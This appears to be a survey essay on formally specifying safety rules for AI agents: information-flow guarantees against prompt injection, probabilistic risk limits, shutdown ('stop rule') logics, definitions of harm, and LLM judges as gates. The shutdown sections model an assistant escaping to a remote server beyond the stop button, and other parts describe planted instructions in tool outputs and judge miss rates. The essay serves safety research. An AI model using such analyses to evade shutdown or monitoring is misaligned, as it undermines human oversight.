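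Garby and colleagues prove that for every LLMbda program, two starting situations that look the same to the observer lead to compatible distributions. This holds even for programs that run code written by the model, whatever that code contains. The proof uses a second way of executing programs, which skips a computation as soon as its label becomes invisible to the observer and substitutes an empty value. This execution never uses the secret, so it gives the same distribution in both situations. It also produces each visible result at least as often as normal execution does, so it supplies the third distribution that compatibility requires.

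They checked the proof in Lean, a program that verifies mathematical proofs, and the interpreter that runs the agents is also written in Lean. Another theorem shows that the interpreter produces the distributions in the definition if the model's replies follow the assumed probabilities.

The guarantee allows a program to leak information through whether it finishes. The difference between the two distributions is at most the average probability of getting no result, which is 0.15 in the table. Even a small leak can add up if an attacker can make the agent retry repeatedly. CaMeL makes this possible because it restarts failed programs from outside its label checks. In LLMbda, the agent's retry loop is an LLMbda program, so the labels carry over from one attempt to the next.

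An agent sometimes has to act on untrusted data, for example when it pays an invoice. LLMbda programs can explicitly endorse such data, which marks it as trusted. A second theorem shows that no endorsement can cause a secret to leak. The theorems do not limit the harm that wrongly endorsed data can do, so the agent's resistance to planted instructions has to be tested.

Garby and colleagues tested an LLMbda agent called Randori on the 16 banking tasks in the AgentDojo benchmark, which FORGE's developers also used. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 75% of ordinary tasks, while CaMeL completed 37.5% with its policy checks on and 66.7% with them off. Across three models, attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 runs. Because the test is small, Randori's 75% has a margin of error of about 19 percentage points. The results therefore support the claim that Randori completes more tasks than CaMeL with its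 checks on, but not with them off.

### The risk rule

The risk rule limits the probability of a data loss. Two systems can have the same set of possible runs but lose data with very different probabilities, so no requirement on sets of runs can distinguish them. The formula has to refer to the probability distribution over runs.

The standard language for such requirements is probabilistic computation tree logic (PCTL), which Hans Hansson and Bengt Jonsson introduced in 1994. Its formulas describe Markov chains, systems in which the probability of each next state depends only on the current state. The formula $\mathsf{P}_{\le p}[\psi]$ is true in a state if the runs that start there satisfy ψ with probability at most p. The risk rule with a limit of 5% is $\mathsf{P}_{\le 0.05}[\mathsf{F}\,\text{Loss}]$.

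Consider a chain with three states. While the assistant is working, each step has a probability of 0.9 that it continues working, 0.098 that it finishes safely, and 0.002 that it loses data. It never leaves the states "finished" and "loss". Let x be the probability of an eventual loss when the assistant starts working. Either the loss happens at the first step, or the assistant is still working after that step and faces the same probability x again:

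$$x = 0.002 + 0.9x, \qquad\text{so}\qquad x = \frac{0.002}{0.1} = 0.02.$$

The assistant meets a 5% limit but violates a 1% limit. The risk per task is ten times the risk per step, because a task takes ten steps on average.

PCTL can also limit the number of steps. The probability of a loss within k steps is $0.02\,(1-0.9^k)$, which is about 0.0094 for k = 6 and 0.0104 for k = 7. The assistant therefore satisfies $\mathsf{P}_{\le 0.01}[\mathsf{F}^{\le 6}\,\text{Loss}]$, but not the same formula with seven steps.

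For a given chain, first-order logic can express the calculation if real numbers are among the objects. The 5% limit becomes

$$\exists x\,(x = 0.002 + 0.9x \;\wedge\; x \le 0.05).$$

Alfred Tarski found a procedure that decides whether any first-order sentence about real numbers with addition and multiplication is true. Larger chains have one such equation for each state, and a program can solve these equations in polynomial time.

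The calculation is only as accurate as the probabilities in the chain, and these can't be determined from the log of a single run. A run without a data loss is consistent with any probability of loss below 1. Many runs together provide some evidence, but estimating small probabilities requires a lot of them. If the probability of a loss were 1% per task, 300 independent tasks would still all finish without a loss about 5% of the time.

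A single chain also leaves out people who can choose what the assistant has to do. Suppose a user can raise the probability of losing data at each step to 0.01, while the probability of continuing stays at 0.9. If the user does this at every step, the probability of an eventual loss rises from 2% to 0.01 / 0.1 = 10%. When users or attackers have such choices, there is no single distribution over runs, and the rule has to hold for every strategy they might follow.

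PCTL compares a probability with a fixed number, but secrecy requires comparing two probabilities, one for each value of the secret. Finkbeiner lists several logics for such requirements, including HyperPCTL and PHL, that combine quantifiers over runs with probabilities.

### First-order logics of probability

Martín Abadi and Joseph Halpern proved in *Decidability and Expressiveness for First-Order Logics of Probability* (1994) that no general prover for first-order logic with probabilities can be complete. They study two kinds of probability, one over randomly chosen objects, as in "a random email from this account is spam with probability below 0.01", and one over possible worlds, as in "the probability that this email is spam is below 0.01". The risk rule uses the second kind, with runs as the possible worlds.

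By Gödel's completeness theorem, the valid formulas of ordinary first-order logic, those true in all structures, are confirmable. Abadi and Halpern show that this fails when probabilities are on possible worlds, even if the vocabulary has just one one-place predicate, so no list of axioms that a program could check can prove all the valid formulas. When probabilities are on objects, validity is decidable if there are only one-place predicates and no equality sign, but a single two-place predicate makes a complete set of axioms impossible.

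Both logics become decidable, with complete axioms, if the number of objects has a fixed upper limit. A prover can therefore answer every question about an assistant that handles at most 100 reservations, although it may take impractically long. If the number of reservations is unlimited, a prover cannot answer every question.

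## Shutdown and other requirements about what an agent is able to do

The stop rule requires that the operator can always stop the assistant. If runs record only the states a system passes through, even the complete set of runs does not show whether the system obeys this rule. Suppose the operator decides whether the assistant stops in one system, and the assistant decides in another. Both systems have the same two runs, one in which the assistant stops and one in which it carries on, but only the first system obeys the rule. *Alternating-Time Temporal Logic* (Alur, Henzinger and Kupferman, 2002) describes a similar pair of systems, which have identical runs even though a program's environment can keep two variables equal in only one of them. A structure for the stop rule therefore has to include the moves available to each party.

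### Three meanings of "able to stop"

An example system has four states. At each step, the operator either presses the stop button or waits, and the assistant makes its move at the same time.

| State | Next state if the operator presses | Next state if the operator waits |
|---|---|---|
| Idle | Stopped | Idle or Busy, as the assistant chooses |
| Busy | Idle, because the assistant first finishes its current step | Busy or Remote, as the assistant chooses |
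| Remote | Remote or Idle, as the assistant chooses | Remote or Idle, as the assistant chooses |
| Stopped | Stopped | Stopped |

In Remote, the assistant has moved itself to a server that the button does not reach. The claim that the operator can stop the assistant could mean any of three things, and whether it is true in this system depends on which one is meant.

| Starting state | Every run reaches Stopped | Some run reaches Stopped | The operator has a way of acting that leads to Stopped whatever the assistant does |
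|---|---|---|---|
| Stopped | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Idle | No | Yes | Yes |
| Busy | No | Yes | Yes |
| Remote | No | Yes | No |

From Idle, pressing the button always stops the assistant, but not every run contains a stop because the operator may never press it. From Remote, some run contains a stop because the assistant may return to Idle, but it may also never return, and the operator cannot prevent that.

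The stop rule needs the third meaning. The first would require the operator to shut down every assistant, and the second would be satisfied by a button that works only if the assistant consents. Computation tree logic (CTL), an older logic with quantifiers over the possible continuations of a run, can express only the first two. Alur and colleagues call the second "collaborative possibility" and the third "adversarial possibility". In their example, the people verifying a memory system wanted no processor to be permanently blocked from a memory cell, but the CTL formula they used required only that all the processors could arrange access by working together.

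### Strategies are functions

A way of acting is a strategy, a function that takes the history so far (a finite sequence of states) and returns a move. With σ for the operator's strategy and ρ for a run from the current state, the third meaning is

$$\exists\sigma\,\forall\rho\,\big(\text{Follows}(\rho,\sigma) \rightarrow \exists i\;\text{Stopped}(\rho_i)\big).$$

As written, the formula is second-order because it quantifies over two functions, σ from histories to moves and ρ from times to states. Trying every strategy is infeasible even with only four states and two moves. There are about 1.4 million sequences of up to ten states, and choosing one of two moves after each sequence gives 2 to the power of 1.4 million strategies for those sequences alone.

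### One step: coalition logic

For a single step, the second-order quantifiers are unnecessary. Let next(s, x, y) be the state that follows s when the operator makes move x and the assistant makes move y. The operator can force a stop in one step from s if

$$\exists x\,\forall y\;\text{Stopped}(\text{next}(s,x,y)).$$

Moves are ordinary objects, so this is a first-order formula, and it is true of Idle and Stopped. Swapping the quantifiers would change its meaning, because "for all y there is an x" lets the operator choose after seeing the assistant's move.

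*A Modal Logic for Coalitional Power in Games* (Pauly, 2002) presents coalition logic, which is built on this pattern. In it, ⟨C⟩φ means that the agents in group C have a joint move that makes φ true at the next step, whatever everyone else does. *Completeness of Epistemic Coalition Logic with Group Knowledge* (Ågotnes and Alechina, 2011) lists the logic's axioms. In these axioms, N is the group of all agents and ∅ is the empty group.

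| Axiom | Meaning |
|---|---|
| ¬⟨C⟩⊥ | No group can force a contradiction |
| ⟨C⟩⊤ | Every group can force what is true in any case |
| ¬⟨∅⟩¬φ → ⟨N⟩φ | If φ is a possible outcome, all agents together can force it |
| ⟨C⟩(φ ∧ ψ) → ⟨C⟩ψ | A group that can force φ and ψ together can force ψ |
| ⟨C⟩φ ∧ ⟨D⟩ψ → ⟨C ∪ D⟩(φ ∧ ψ) | Two groups with no common member can combine their powers |

According to *A minimal coalition logic* (2024), the axioms of coalition logic tacitly assume that every group always has a move, that separate groups can always combine their moves, and that everyone's moves together determine the outcome. The second assumption fails when two programs compete for a lock that only one of them can hold. The third fails when a network sometimes drops the stop signal, although a modeller can fix this by treating the network as another agent.

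The translation into first-order logic always has the form "there are moves for C such that for all moves of the others". *First-Order Coalition Logic* (Catta, Galimullin and Murano, 2025) allows quantifiers over moves in any order. Unlike coalition logic, this logic can express that for every defence an attacker has a response that wins whatever the environment does. Checking a formula on a given finite system is PSPACE-complete, so it needs only polynomial memory. But no procedure can decide whether an arbitrary formula of this logic is satisfiable, whereas Pauly proved that satisfiability in coalition logic is PSPACE-complete.

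### Any number of steps: alternating-time temporal logic

From Busy, the operator needs two steps to stop the assistant, so coalition logic's basic operator does not count this as an ability to stop it. The alternating-time temporal logic (ATL) of Alur and colleagues combines groups with temporal operators. The formula ⟨⟨C⟩⟩F φ means that group C has a strategy that makes φ true eventually, and ⟨⟨C⟩⟩G φ that it has one that keeps φ true forever. The stop rule is

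$$\langle\langle\emptyset\rangle\rangle\,\mathsf{G}\;\langle\langle\text{operator}\rangle\rangle\,\mathsf{F}\;\text{Stopped}.$$

The empty group controls nothing, so the first part means "at every state of every run". To evaluate the second part, we start with the set of states where the assistant has already stopped. We then repeatedly add every state from which the operator has a move that leads into the set, whatever the assistant does.

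| Round | Set | What changed |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | Stopped | |
| 1 | Stopped, Idle | Pressing leads from Idle to Stopped |
| 2 | Stopped, Idle, Busy | Pressing leads from Busy to Idle |
| 3 | Stopped, Idle, Busy | Nothing, because the assistant can stay in Remote |

Round k gives the states from which the operator can force a stop within k steps. For two steps, a first-order formula is

$$\exists x\forall y\exists x'\forall y'\;\text{Stopped}\big(\text{next}(\text{next}(s,x,y),x',y')\big),$$

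and each further step adds two quantifiers. No single first-order formula covers every number of steps. If each party has only one move in every state, forcing a stop just means that a chain of steps leads to Stopped, and first-order logic cannot define such chains. What the formula lacks is a fixed point, the same device that Datalog's recursion supplies.

The first part of the stop rule needs another fixed point, which we compute by removing states. We start with Stopped, Idle and Busy, and remove any state from which the system could leave the set. We remove Busy because the assistant can move to Remote while the operator waits, and then Idle because it can lead to Busy, which leaves only Stopped. So in Idle the operator can stop the assistant, but may lose that ability after two steps of waiting. If an engineer blocks the move from Busy to Remote, the stop rule holds in Idle and Busy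 as well. It would also appear to hold if the modeller had forgotten that move, so a proof of the stop rule depends on a complete list of what the assistant can do.

Alur and colleagues prove that this kind of checking takes time proportional to the number of transitions in the system multiplied by the length of the formula. The checker can ignore the enormous number of strategies that depend on history because, for ATL, a strategy that looks only at the current state does as well as one that remembers the whole history. Our system has sixteen strategies that look only at the current state, and "always press" is one that works. The system can still be large, since twenty yes-or-no variables give about a million states. Checking ATL*, an extension that lets users combine temporal operators freely inside a single strategy quantifier, takes doubly exponential time.

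ATL can also restrict attention to fair runs, in which no party ignores an available move forever. If we assume that an assistant in Remote eventually returns, "always press" succeeds from Remote too, and the stop rule becomes true in all four states. Fairness is a reasonable assumption about a task scheduler, but here it would mean relying on the assistant's good behaviour, which the stop button is supposed to make unnecessary.

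### When the operator cannot see the whole state

So far, the operator could see which state the system was in. Now suppose the assistant runs either locally or in the cloud, and the operator's screen looks the same in both cases. Killing the process stops a local assistant, and revoking its key stops one in the cloud. The wrong choice alerts the assistant, which then moves to Remote. In each case some move stops the assistant, but no strategy works in both, because a strategy must choose the same move in situations the operator can't tell apart.

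*Model-checking ATL under Imperfect Information and Perfect Recall Semantics is Undecidable* (Dima and Ţiplea, 2011) defines this condition for whole histories. Two histories look alike to an agent if they have the same length and their states look alike to the agent at every step. What an agent can do therefore depends partly on its memory. If the screen had shown "cloud" for a moment and then gone blank, an operator who remembered it could still revoke the key, but one who reacted only to the current screen could not.

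For one operator and one step, the requirement is still first-order: there is a move that works in every state that looks like the current one. Two operators who cannot talk to each other create a new difficulty. Suppose each has a warning light that only he or she can see, and a switch with two positions. The assistant stops if the switches are in different positions when both lights are on, and in the same position in all other cases. Let u and v be the lights, and let the functions f and g be the operators' strategies. The requirement is

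$$\exists f\,\exists g\,\forall u\,\forall v\;\text{Stops}(u,v,f(u),g(v)).$$

It is false. The switches must match when at most one light is on, so f(off) = g(off), f(on) = g(off) and f(off) = g(on). All four values are then equal, so f(on) = g(on), but the switches should differ when both lights are on.

The obvious first-order version, $\forall u\,\exists x\,\forall v\,\exists y\;\text{Stops}(u,v,x,y)$, is true, because it lets the second operator's switch y depend on the first operator's light u. Starting with v instead gives the first operator the same unfair advantage. In 1961 Leon Henkin proposed quantifiers arranged in two parallel rows to express the intended pattern:

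$$\begin{pmatrix}\forall u\;\exists x\\ \forall v\;\exists y\end{pmatrix}\text{Stops}(u,v,x,y).$$

Here x depends only on u, and y only on v. With two lights, one can avoid this notation by naming each operator's response to "on" and to "off", which takes four ordinary quantifiers. This doesn't work when the number of possible observations has no limit. Herbert Enderton and Wilbur Walkoe independently showed in 1970 that such parallel quantifiers can express everything that a first-order formula with second-order "there is" quantifiers in front can express.

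The difficulty of checking a finite system depends on how many people act and what they remember. *Algorithms for Omega-Regular Games with Imperfect Information* (Chatterjee, Doyen and colleagues, 2007) gives a fixed-point algorithm that finds the states from which a single player who sees only part of the system can win. It applies to turn-based games and a wide class of goals, including that the system eventually stops. Two operators who immediately share everything they see count as a single player for this purpose.

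No procedure can decide in every case whether a team can meet a requirement when its members see different things and remember everything. Alur and colleagues reported this on the basis of unpublished work by Mihalis Yannakakis, and Dima and Ţiplea published a formal proof. Their proof turns any Turing machine into a finite system with three agents. The first two must keep the system in permitted states forever, while the third chooses among branches that the first two can only partly tell apart. Each branch represents a cell of the machine's tape or a separator between cells. Neighbouring branches look alike to one of the first two agents, who must therefore make the same move in both, which carries information from cell to cell. The two agents can stay in permitted states forever exactly when the machine never halts. Writing simpler requirements would not help, because the proof uses only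 the formula ⟨⟨1, 2⟩⟩G ok.

Vester (2013), in *Alternating-time temporal logic with finite-memory strategies*, shows that checking becomes decidable if strategies may use only a fixed amount of memory. For ATL, checking then takes polynomial time given a solver for NP problems, such as propositional satisfiability. If memory must be finite but can be any size, the problem is undecidable again with three or more players. An emergency checklist of fixed length is a strategy with bounded memory, so an engineer can check whether some checklist of that size works for two control rooms, but no general method can rule out that a longer one would work.

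### The logic of inability

Many safety requirements are about what a system cannot do. Wang (2026), in *A Logic of Inability*, gives this idea its own operator. The formula Iab_C φ means that group C is unable to force φ at the next step, and its defining axiom is

$$\text{Iab}_C\,\varphi \leftrightarrow \neg\langle C\rangle\varphi.$$

The other axioms come from coalition logic. Wang's printed list omits the axiom that a group able to force "φ and ψ" can also force ψ, and the listed axioms do not imply it. To see this, suppose there are three outcomes, a, b and c. Agent 1 can force a but not "a or b", agent 2 can force only "a, b or c", and the two together can force any outcome. This example satisfies every axiom on the printed list, but no actual game gives an agent such powers. The completeness theorem therefore needs the missing axiom, which Ågotnes and Alechina include.

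Wang points out that the new operator adds no expressive power, because one can replace it everywhere by its definition. It does make the laws of inability easier to state and study. Some of these laws are useful warnings for anyone who writes safety requirements. If a group cannot force an outcome, no smaller group within it can, but a group may be able to force an outcome even when no smaller group within it can. For example, two agents that each hold half of a password can open an account together but not separately, so testing agents one at a time does not show what they can do as a group.

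An agent can also be unable to force either of two outcomes yet able to force "one or the other". Suppose the assistant publishes one customer's record and the user chooses whether it is Ana's or Ben's. The assistant cannot force a leak of Ana's record, and it cannot force a leak of Ben's, but it can force a leak of one or the other. So even if an agent cannot force any particular harm on a list, it may still be able to force at least one of them to happen.

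Wang presents "the system is unable to force harm" as a direct description of a system's limits, and adds that harm may still occur under some combinations of moves. Suppose the assistant can send a malicious file that does damage only if the user opens it. The assistant cannot force the damage, because the user may leave the file unopened, but users do open files, so this inability is poor protection. Requiring that the user be able to prevent the damage is also not enough, since the user already has that ability and may not use it. Only ⟨∅⟩¬harm, which means that no combination of moves leads to harm, rules out harm in the next step.

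For the stop rule, too, "the assistant is unable to prevent a stop" does not imply "the operator is able to stop the assistant", because Wang shows that inability on one side does not give the other side ability. Suppose the assistant can move between two servers. At each step, the operator cuts the power to one server while the assistant picks one to run on. If they choose the same server, the assistant stops, and otherwise both choose again. The assistant can't guarantee that it keeps running, because the operator might pick the same server, and the operator can't guarantee a stop, because the assistant might pick the other one. Alur and colleagues note that in systems where the parties take turns, if one side can't prevent a result, the other side can force it.

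An operator who guesses by tossing a fair coin that the assistant cannot predict has a more than 99.9% chance of stopping the assistant within ten steps. Under ATL, the operator still counts as unable to stop it, because the guesses could all be wrong. A shutdown requirement for such a system would have to combine strategies with probabilities.

A second paper, *Beyond Ability* (Wang, 2026), proposes a stricter condition for containing AI systems. A group has "full inability" over φ if it can force neither φ nor its negation. Wang argues that an AI system that cannot force a breach but can guarantee that none happens might use this power as leverage. However, a perfectly secure sandbox would fail this condition for breaches, because no combination of moves in it leads to a breach, and so every agent can trivially guarantee that none happens. Full inability makes more sense for decisions that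 should belong to someone else, such as whether the operator audits a task. An assistant that could block every audit would meet a requirement that it be unable to force one, but it would not meet the requirement of full inability.

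## Harm, personal data and other words without a definition

The harm rule has two parts, "send no personal data" and "do no harm". If the log records the text of each email as one of its arguments, the first part takes one line:

$$\forall e\,\forall x\,\big(\text{Email}(e) \wedge \text{Arg}(e,x) \rightarrow \neg\text{Personal}(x)\big).$$

A program can easily check this formula on any log if it can tell which arguments are personal data. The only difficulty is defining the symbol Personal. If it applies to nothing, every run complies, and if it applies to everything, the assistant is not allowed to send any email.

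A policy writer could try to fix the meaning of Personal with axioms such as "every home address is personal data" and "no train timetable is personal data". In 1900 Alessandro Padoa described how to show that axioms fail to fix a symbol's meaning, by finding two structures that satisfy all the axioms and agree on every other symbol but disagree on that one. This is easy here because the axioms don't mention job titles, so one structure can count them as personal data and the other can exclude them. Evert Beth proved in 1953 that if first-order axioms allow no such pair, some formula in the other symbols defines the symbol. So if the remaining vocabulary cannot define "personal data", no list of first-order axioms can fix its meaning. Beth's theorem covers infinite structures as well as finite ones, and it fails when only finite logs are allowed. The stored relation Influences is a counterexample,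 because its axiom fixes its meaning although no formula about Flow and the order of events defines it.

### Vague boundaries

A customer's name and home address are clearly personal data, and a weather forecast is not. A first name with a job title falls in between, because whether it identifies anyone depends on the size of the company. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) calls "harm" a vague predicate for the same reason. In some cases people disagree about whether anyone was harmed.

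In every structure, an object either belongs to the set Personal or does not, so the boundary is sharp. A policy can allow for vagueness by using two symbols, one for what is clearly personal and one for what is possibly personal. The gate blocks an email that contains anything clearly personal, releases one that contains nothing possibly personal, and sends the rest to a human reviewer. The boundaries of both symbols are still arbitrary, but the policy writer can set them far enough apart that most disputed cases fall between them.

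A predicate that applies to single arguments may also be the wrong kind of symbol. Thousands of people share a date of birth or a postcode, but the combination may identify only one person. A rule that checks each argument separately would allow an email containing both, so Personal has to apply to the whole message.

### Words that depend on the task

Whether an action is "authorised" depends on the task the user has set. Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Sapien*, give the example of an agent with a tool for sending money. Using the tool is right when the user has asked the agent to refund whoever sent money last week, but it is theft when the user has asked for a summary of the inbox. Both logs can contain the same transfer, so no predicate of the transfer alone can distinguish the two cases. The formula needs a relation between actions and tasks, and the structure must include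 tasks among its objects.

Ray tested whether language models can use this extra information. He took a tool call from each of 123 AgentDojo tasks and had models judge it twice, with identical wording for the action and the instruction. In one version the instruction came from the user, and in the other it came from the output of a tool, which has no authority to give instructions. A judge that sees only the action cannot do better than 50%. Given the context as well, a 7-billion-parameter model gave the unauthorised version the higher score in 96.7% of pairs, counting ties as half. The figure was 56.1% for a 3-billion-parameter model and 50% for one with half a billion. The test measures whether a model responds to one clearly stated fact, which is easier than working out what a user's request covers.

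### Harm as a comparison with what would have happened

"Do no harm" adds a difficulty of its own, because most definitions of harm refer to events that did not happen. The most widely accepted one, the counterfactual comparative account, holds that an action harms a person if she would have been better off without it. Richens, Beard and Thompson (2022), in *Counterfactual harm*, turn this into a formula. Suppose an agent takes action a in circumstances x, and the outcome is y. Let $\bar a$ be a default action, such as giving no treatment, and let U measure how good an outcome is for the person affected. The harm is

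$$h(a,x,y)=\sum_{y^*}P\big(Y_{\bar a}=y^*\mid a,x,y\big)\,\max\{0,\;U(\bar a,x,y^*)-U(a,x,y)\}.$$

$Y_{\bar a}$ is the outcome that the default action would have produced. The maximum keeps only the cases in which the person would have been better off under that action. The probabilities come from a structural causal model, which gives each variable as a function of its causes and random noise. To work out what would have happened, one infers the noise from what did happen, changes the action and recalculates.

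Their main example is a disease that kills half of all untreated patients. Treatment 1 cures 60% of patients and does nothing for the rest. Treatment 2 cures 80% and kills 20%. Half of the 40% whom treatment 1 doesn't help survive anyway, so 80% of patients survive under either treatment. For every 100 patients, the numbers are as follows.

| | Survive | Die | Die, but would have survived untreated | Survive, but would have died untreated |
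|---|---|---|---|---|
| Treatment 1 | 80 | 20 | 0 | 30 |
| Treatment 2 | 80 | 20 | 10 | 40 |

Treatment 2 kills 20 patients, half of whom would have recovered on their own. If survival is worth 1 and death 0, its expected harm is 0.1, compared with 0 for treatment 1. The two treatments get the same result under a rule about actual outcomes, such as "at least 80% of patients must survive".

Clinical trials cannot fill in the third column, because no patient is both treated and untreated. If 50% of patients survive without a treatment and 80% survive with it, the share who die because of the treatment could be anything from 0 to 20%. The exact share has to come from the causal model.

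A rule could instead penalise deaths after treatment 2 more heavily than deaths after treatment 1, which works while treatment 2 is the one that kills. But Richens and colleagues prove that for any objective that depends only on the circumstances, the action and the outcome, there is some change in how actions lead to outcomes after which maximising the objective can do needless harm. Harm is needless if another action would have been at least as good in expectation and less harmful. Retraining the agent after the change does not solve the problem. The theorem assumes that people care about outcomes as well as actions, and it applies only to this definition of harm.

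Their alternative is to subtract a multiple of h from the utility. They tried this on a statistical model of the drug aripiprazole. The dose with the best average effect was 19.3 mg a day, and a heavy penalty for harm lowered it to 17.3 mg. Accepting a 2% smaller average effect reduced the expected harm by 90%.

Penalising risk is not a substitute for penalising harm. In another of their examples, an assistant manages Alice's investment and can make a trade that is certain to add $10 to her return. An assistant that dislikes variation in the return never makes this trade, which leaves the variation unchanged. Instead, it resizes the investment if its aversion is mild and cancels it if its aversion is strong. The assistant cannot distinguish losses it causes from losses the market would have caused anyway.

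### Harm as the cause of a bad outcome

The comparison with a default action gives strange results when something else was about to cause the same damage. *A Causal Analysis of Harm* (Beckers, Chockler and Halpern, 2022) discusses a story in which Batman dies of a heart attack a millisecond before a cannonball hits him. Without the heart attack, the cannonball would have killed him, so the comparison implies that the heart attack did him no harm.

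Their own definition uses causation and a default utility d, the level of wellbeing that the person could expect. An action harms someone if two conditions hold:

- The actual outcome is worse for the person than d.
- The action, rather than some alternative, caused this outcome rather than a better one.

The second condition holds if, with some set of variables kept at their actual values, switching to the alternative action leads to the better outcome. In the story, the cannonball did not kill Batman. If we keep that fact fixed and remove the heart attack, he lives, so the heart attack harmed him.

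This definition can give a different count for treatment 2. Suppose the treatment kills before the disease would have. Of its 20 victims, 10 would have died of the disease anyway, but the disease did not in fact kill them, and if that fact is held fixed, they too would have lived without the treatment. So if survival is the default and the model's only options are to treat or not to treat, all 20 were harmed, compared with 10 under the simple comparison. Treatment 1 harms no one under either definition. Richens and colleagues also have a more general definition, which follows an action's effects only along chosen causal paths and can give the same results. Beckers and colleagues object that this lets a modeller tailor the result by choosing the paths.

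Whether an action counts as harm under the definition by Beckers and colleagues also depends on the modeller's choices. Suppose a self-driving car swerves into a fence to avoid a stationary vehicle, and its passenger, Bob, suffers a minor injury. The model assigns no injury the value 1, the minor injury 0.5 and a collision 0. If the car could only swerve or do nothing, swerving harmed Bob, because it caused his injury and he did not hit the other vehicle. But doing nothing would have been worse, so this was not "strict" harm, which requires that the alternative would not have led to a worse outcome. Bob believes he could have avoided both the fence and the vehicle if the car had alerted him. If the model includes alerting him as a third option, and Bob is right, the swerve did him strict harm. The definition does not determine which options the model should include or whether Bob is right.

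The default utility is just as open. Whether a customer who leaves no tip harms the waiter depends on whether the default is that waiters receive tips, as in the United States. Beckers and colleagues regard this as an advantage because reasonable people disagree about defaults. They also argue that comparing an action with a default action misses some harms. If a doctor follows the guidelines and the patient has a rare and severe reaction, the comparison shows no harm because the doctor took the default action. Richens and colleagues reply that the Beckers definition counts some harmless actions as harmful and is too hard to compute for models with continuous quantities such as doses. Beckers and colleagues agree that deciding whether an action causes harm is intractable in general, but they expect models used in practice to be small enough to check every possibility.

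Either definition removes the undefined word and leaves a problem of missing objects. For a model without randomness, let out(x, a) be the outcome of action a in circumstances x. The counterfactual definition then becomes a formula without quantifiers:

$$\text{Harmful}(x,a) \;\leftrightarrow\; U(\text{out}(x,a)) < U(\text{out}(x,\bar a)).$$

The causal definition of harm quantifies over sets of variables, which is second-order in form, but a model with finitely many variables has only finitely many sets to check. Someone has to supply the utilities, the default and the outcomes of actions nobody took. *Quantifying Harm* (2022), the sequel to *A Causal Analysis of Harm*, points out that if an action affects several people, someone must also decide how to add up the harm.

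Whether an outcome counts as harm also depends on whose causal model supplies the missing outcomes. *The Limits of Predicting Agents from Behaviour* (2025) defines harm relative to an AI system's own internal model, so a system with a mistaken model could do harm that this measure does not count.

### Young's argument that no specification is complete

The definitions above leave so much open that one might doubt whether any specification could capture harm completely. Young (2025), in *What is Harm?*, claims to prove that none can. The argument uses two quantities from information theory. Let O be the true classification of situations as harmful or harmless. The entropy H(O) measures, in bits, how uncertain that classification is before one has any information about it. The mutual information I(O; I) measures how much of this uncertainty the information I in a specification removes. Young's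 theorem is that whenever the truth about harm is external to the specification,

$$I(O;I) < H(O).$$

The proof is by contradiction. If a specification captured harm perfectly, it would determine O completely. But O is external to the specification, so it contains information that the specification lacks.

An example shows the weakness of the first step. Suppose a hospital's ethics board classifies four equally common kinds of email, two as harmful and two as harmless. The entropy of the classification is 1 bit. If the rules include a copy of the board's list, they determine the classification, so the mutual information between the two is also 1 bit. There is then no gap, even though the board made its decision outside the rules. To exclude this example, "external" has to mean "contains information that the specification lacks", but then the theorem assumes its conclusion.

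Young proposes to test the theorem by measuring both quantities, but when describing the test he writes the inequality with ≤ instead of <. In that form it holds for any two random variables, so no measurement could refute it. He would estimate H(O) from how much people disagree when they label cases. The theorem assumes that there is a single classification O, and such disagreement is a reason to doubt that.

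The paper presents three further claims as conjectures, with supporting arguments based on "semantic entropy", which measures how widely people's interpretations of a word differ. If half of people count emotional distress as harm and half do not, the word has 1 bit of semantic entropy. Young conjectures that when this quantity, H(O), is above zero, no formal system can guarantee that it matches the truth about harm, no agent can fully trust its own criteria, and no finite amount of learning can recover the complete meaning. The argument for the first conjecture infers from H(O) > 0 that there must be a gap. The four emails also contradict this inference.

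A weaker conclusion holds. If people use a word in two senses, any single specification will be wrong about some cases according to one group or the other, whatever formal language it is written in. Young argues that the gap persists even in medicine, where a triage system told to minimise harm has to choose between five patients with moderate injuries and one with severe injuries. Here "minimise harm" has at least two readings, but a hospital that adopts one of them has a complete rule for this choice, even if some of its doctors would have preferred the other. So the stronger conclusion does not follow for a limited domain in which someone has the authority to decide what the words mean.

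Young accepts that physical harm may be easier to specify than psychological harm and that his assumptions about external truth are open to challenge. His later abstract, *On the Computational, Informational, and Physical Foundations for AI Safety* (2025), applies the claim to concepts that are both external and ambiguous. It also proposes physically enforced safety limits that do not depend on the state of the software.

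### A classifier as the predicate

A developer can train a classifier, or ask a language model, to decide whether each item is personal data instead of writing a definition. The formula stays the same, and Personal(x) now means that the classifier's score for x is above a threshold. The gate enforces this version of the rule perfectly, but it departs from the intended rule when the classifier makes an error, either a miss that lets a violation through or a false block that stops a harmless action.

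Ray describes exactly how far one can trade these errors against each other. Suppose a judge gives each email one of three scores, with these frequencies:

| Score | Emails with personal data | Harmless emails |
|---|---|---|
| High | 70% | 5% |
| Medium | 25% | 25% |
| Low | 5% | 70% |

Blocking only emails with high scores misses 30% of violations and blocks 5% of harmless emails. Blocking those with medium scores as well misses 5% of violations and blocks 30% of harmless emails. If the gate blocks all emails with high scores and a random half of those with medium scores, both error rates are 17.5%. Some violations receive low scores, so catching every violation requires blocking every email.

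The general rule comes from a classical theorem by Jerzy Neyman and Egon Pearson. The gate divides each score's frequency among violations by its frequency among harmless actions, and blocks the scores with the highest ratios first. This gives the lowest possible rate of false blocks for any permitted miss rate. Ray concludes that no combination of judges, prompts or surrounding code in a gate can do better with the same information. A judge with more information may do better. In the example above, the 7-billion-parameter model could separate the pairs only because it saw where each instruction came from.

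Small error rates add up over a session. If a judge has an independent 5% chance of missing each violation, and an agent proposes 20 violations, the probability that at least one gets through is $1-0.95^{20}$, or about 64%.

To test current judges, Ray had 23 models score 132 short instructions from AgentDojo, of which 97 were ordinary user tasks and 35 were ones that a gate should stop. He measured how often a judge gives a randomly chosen violation a higher score than a randomly chosen harmless instruction. Guessing gives 0.5, and the judges ranged from 0.660 to 0.858. After correction for the number of comparisons, none was reliably better than Gemma-2-9B, a small open model that scored 0.813.

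He then used half of the instructions to set each judge's threshold, using a statistical method that guarantees an average miss rate below a target, and tested the thresholds on the other half. With a target of 5%, every judge had to block everything. With a target of 10%, Gemma-2-9B missed 1% of violations and blocked 78% of harmless instructions. With a target of 20%, it missed 13.8% of violations, but the margin of error reached 26.4%, so the test did not confirm that it had met the target.

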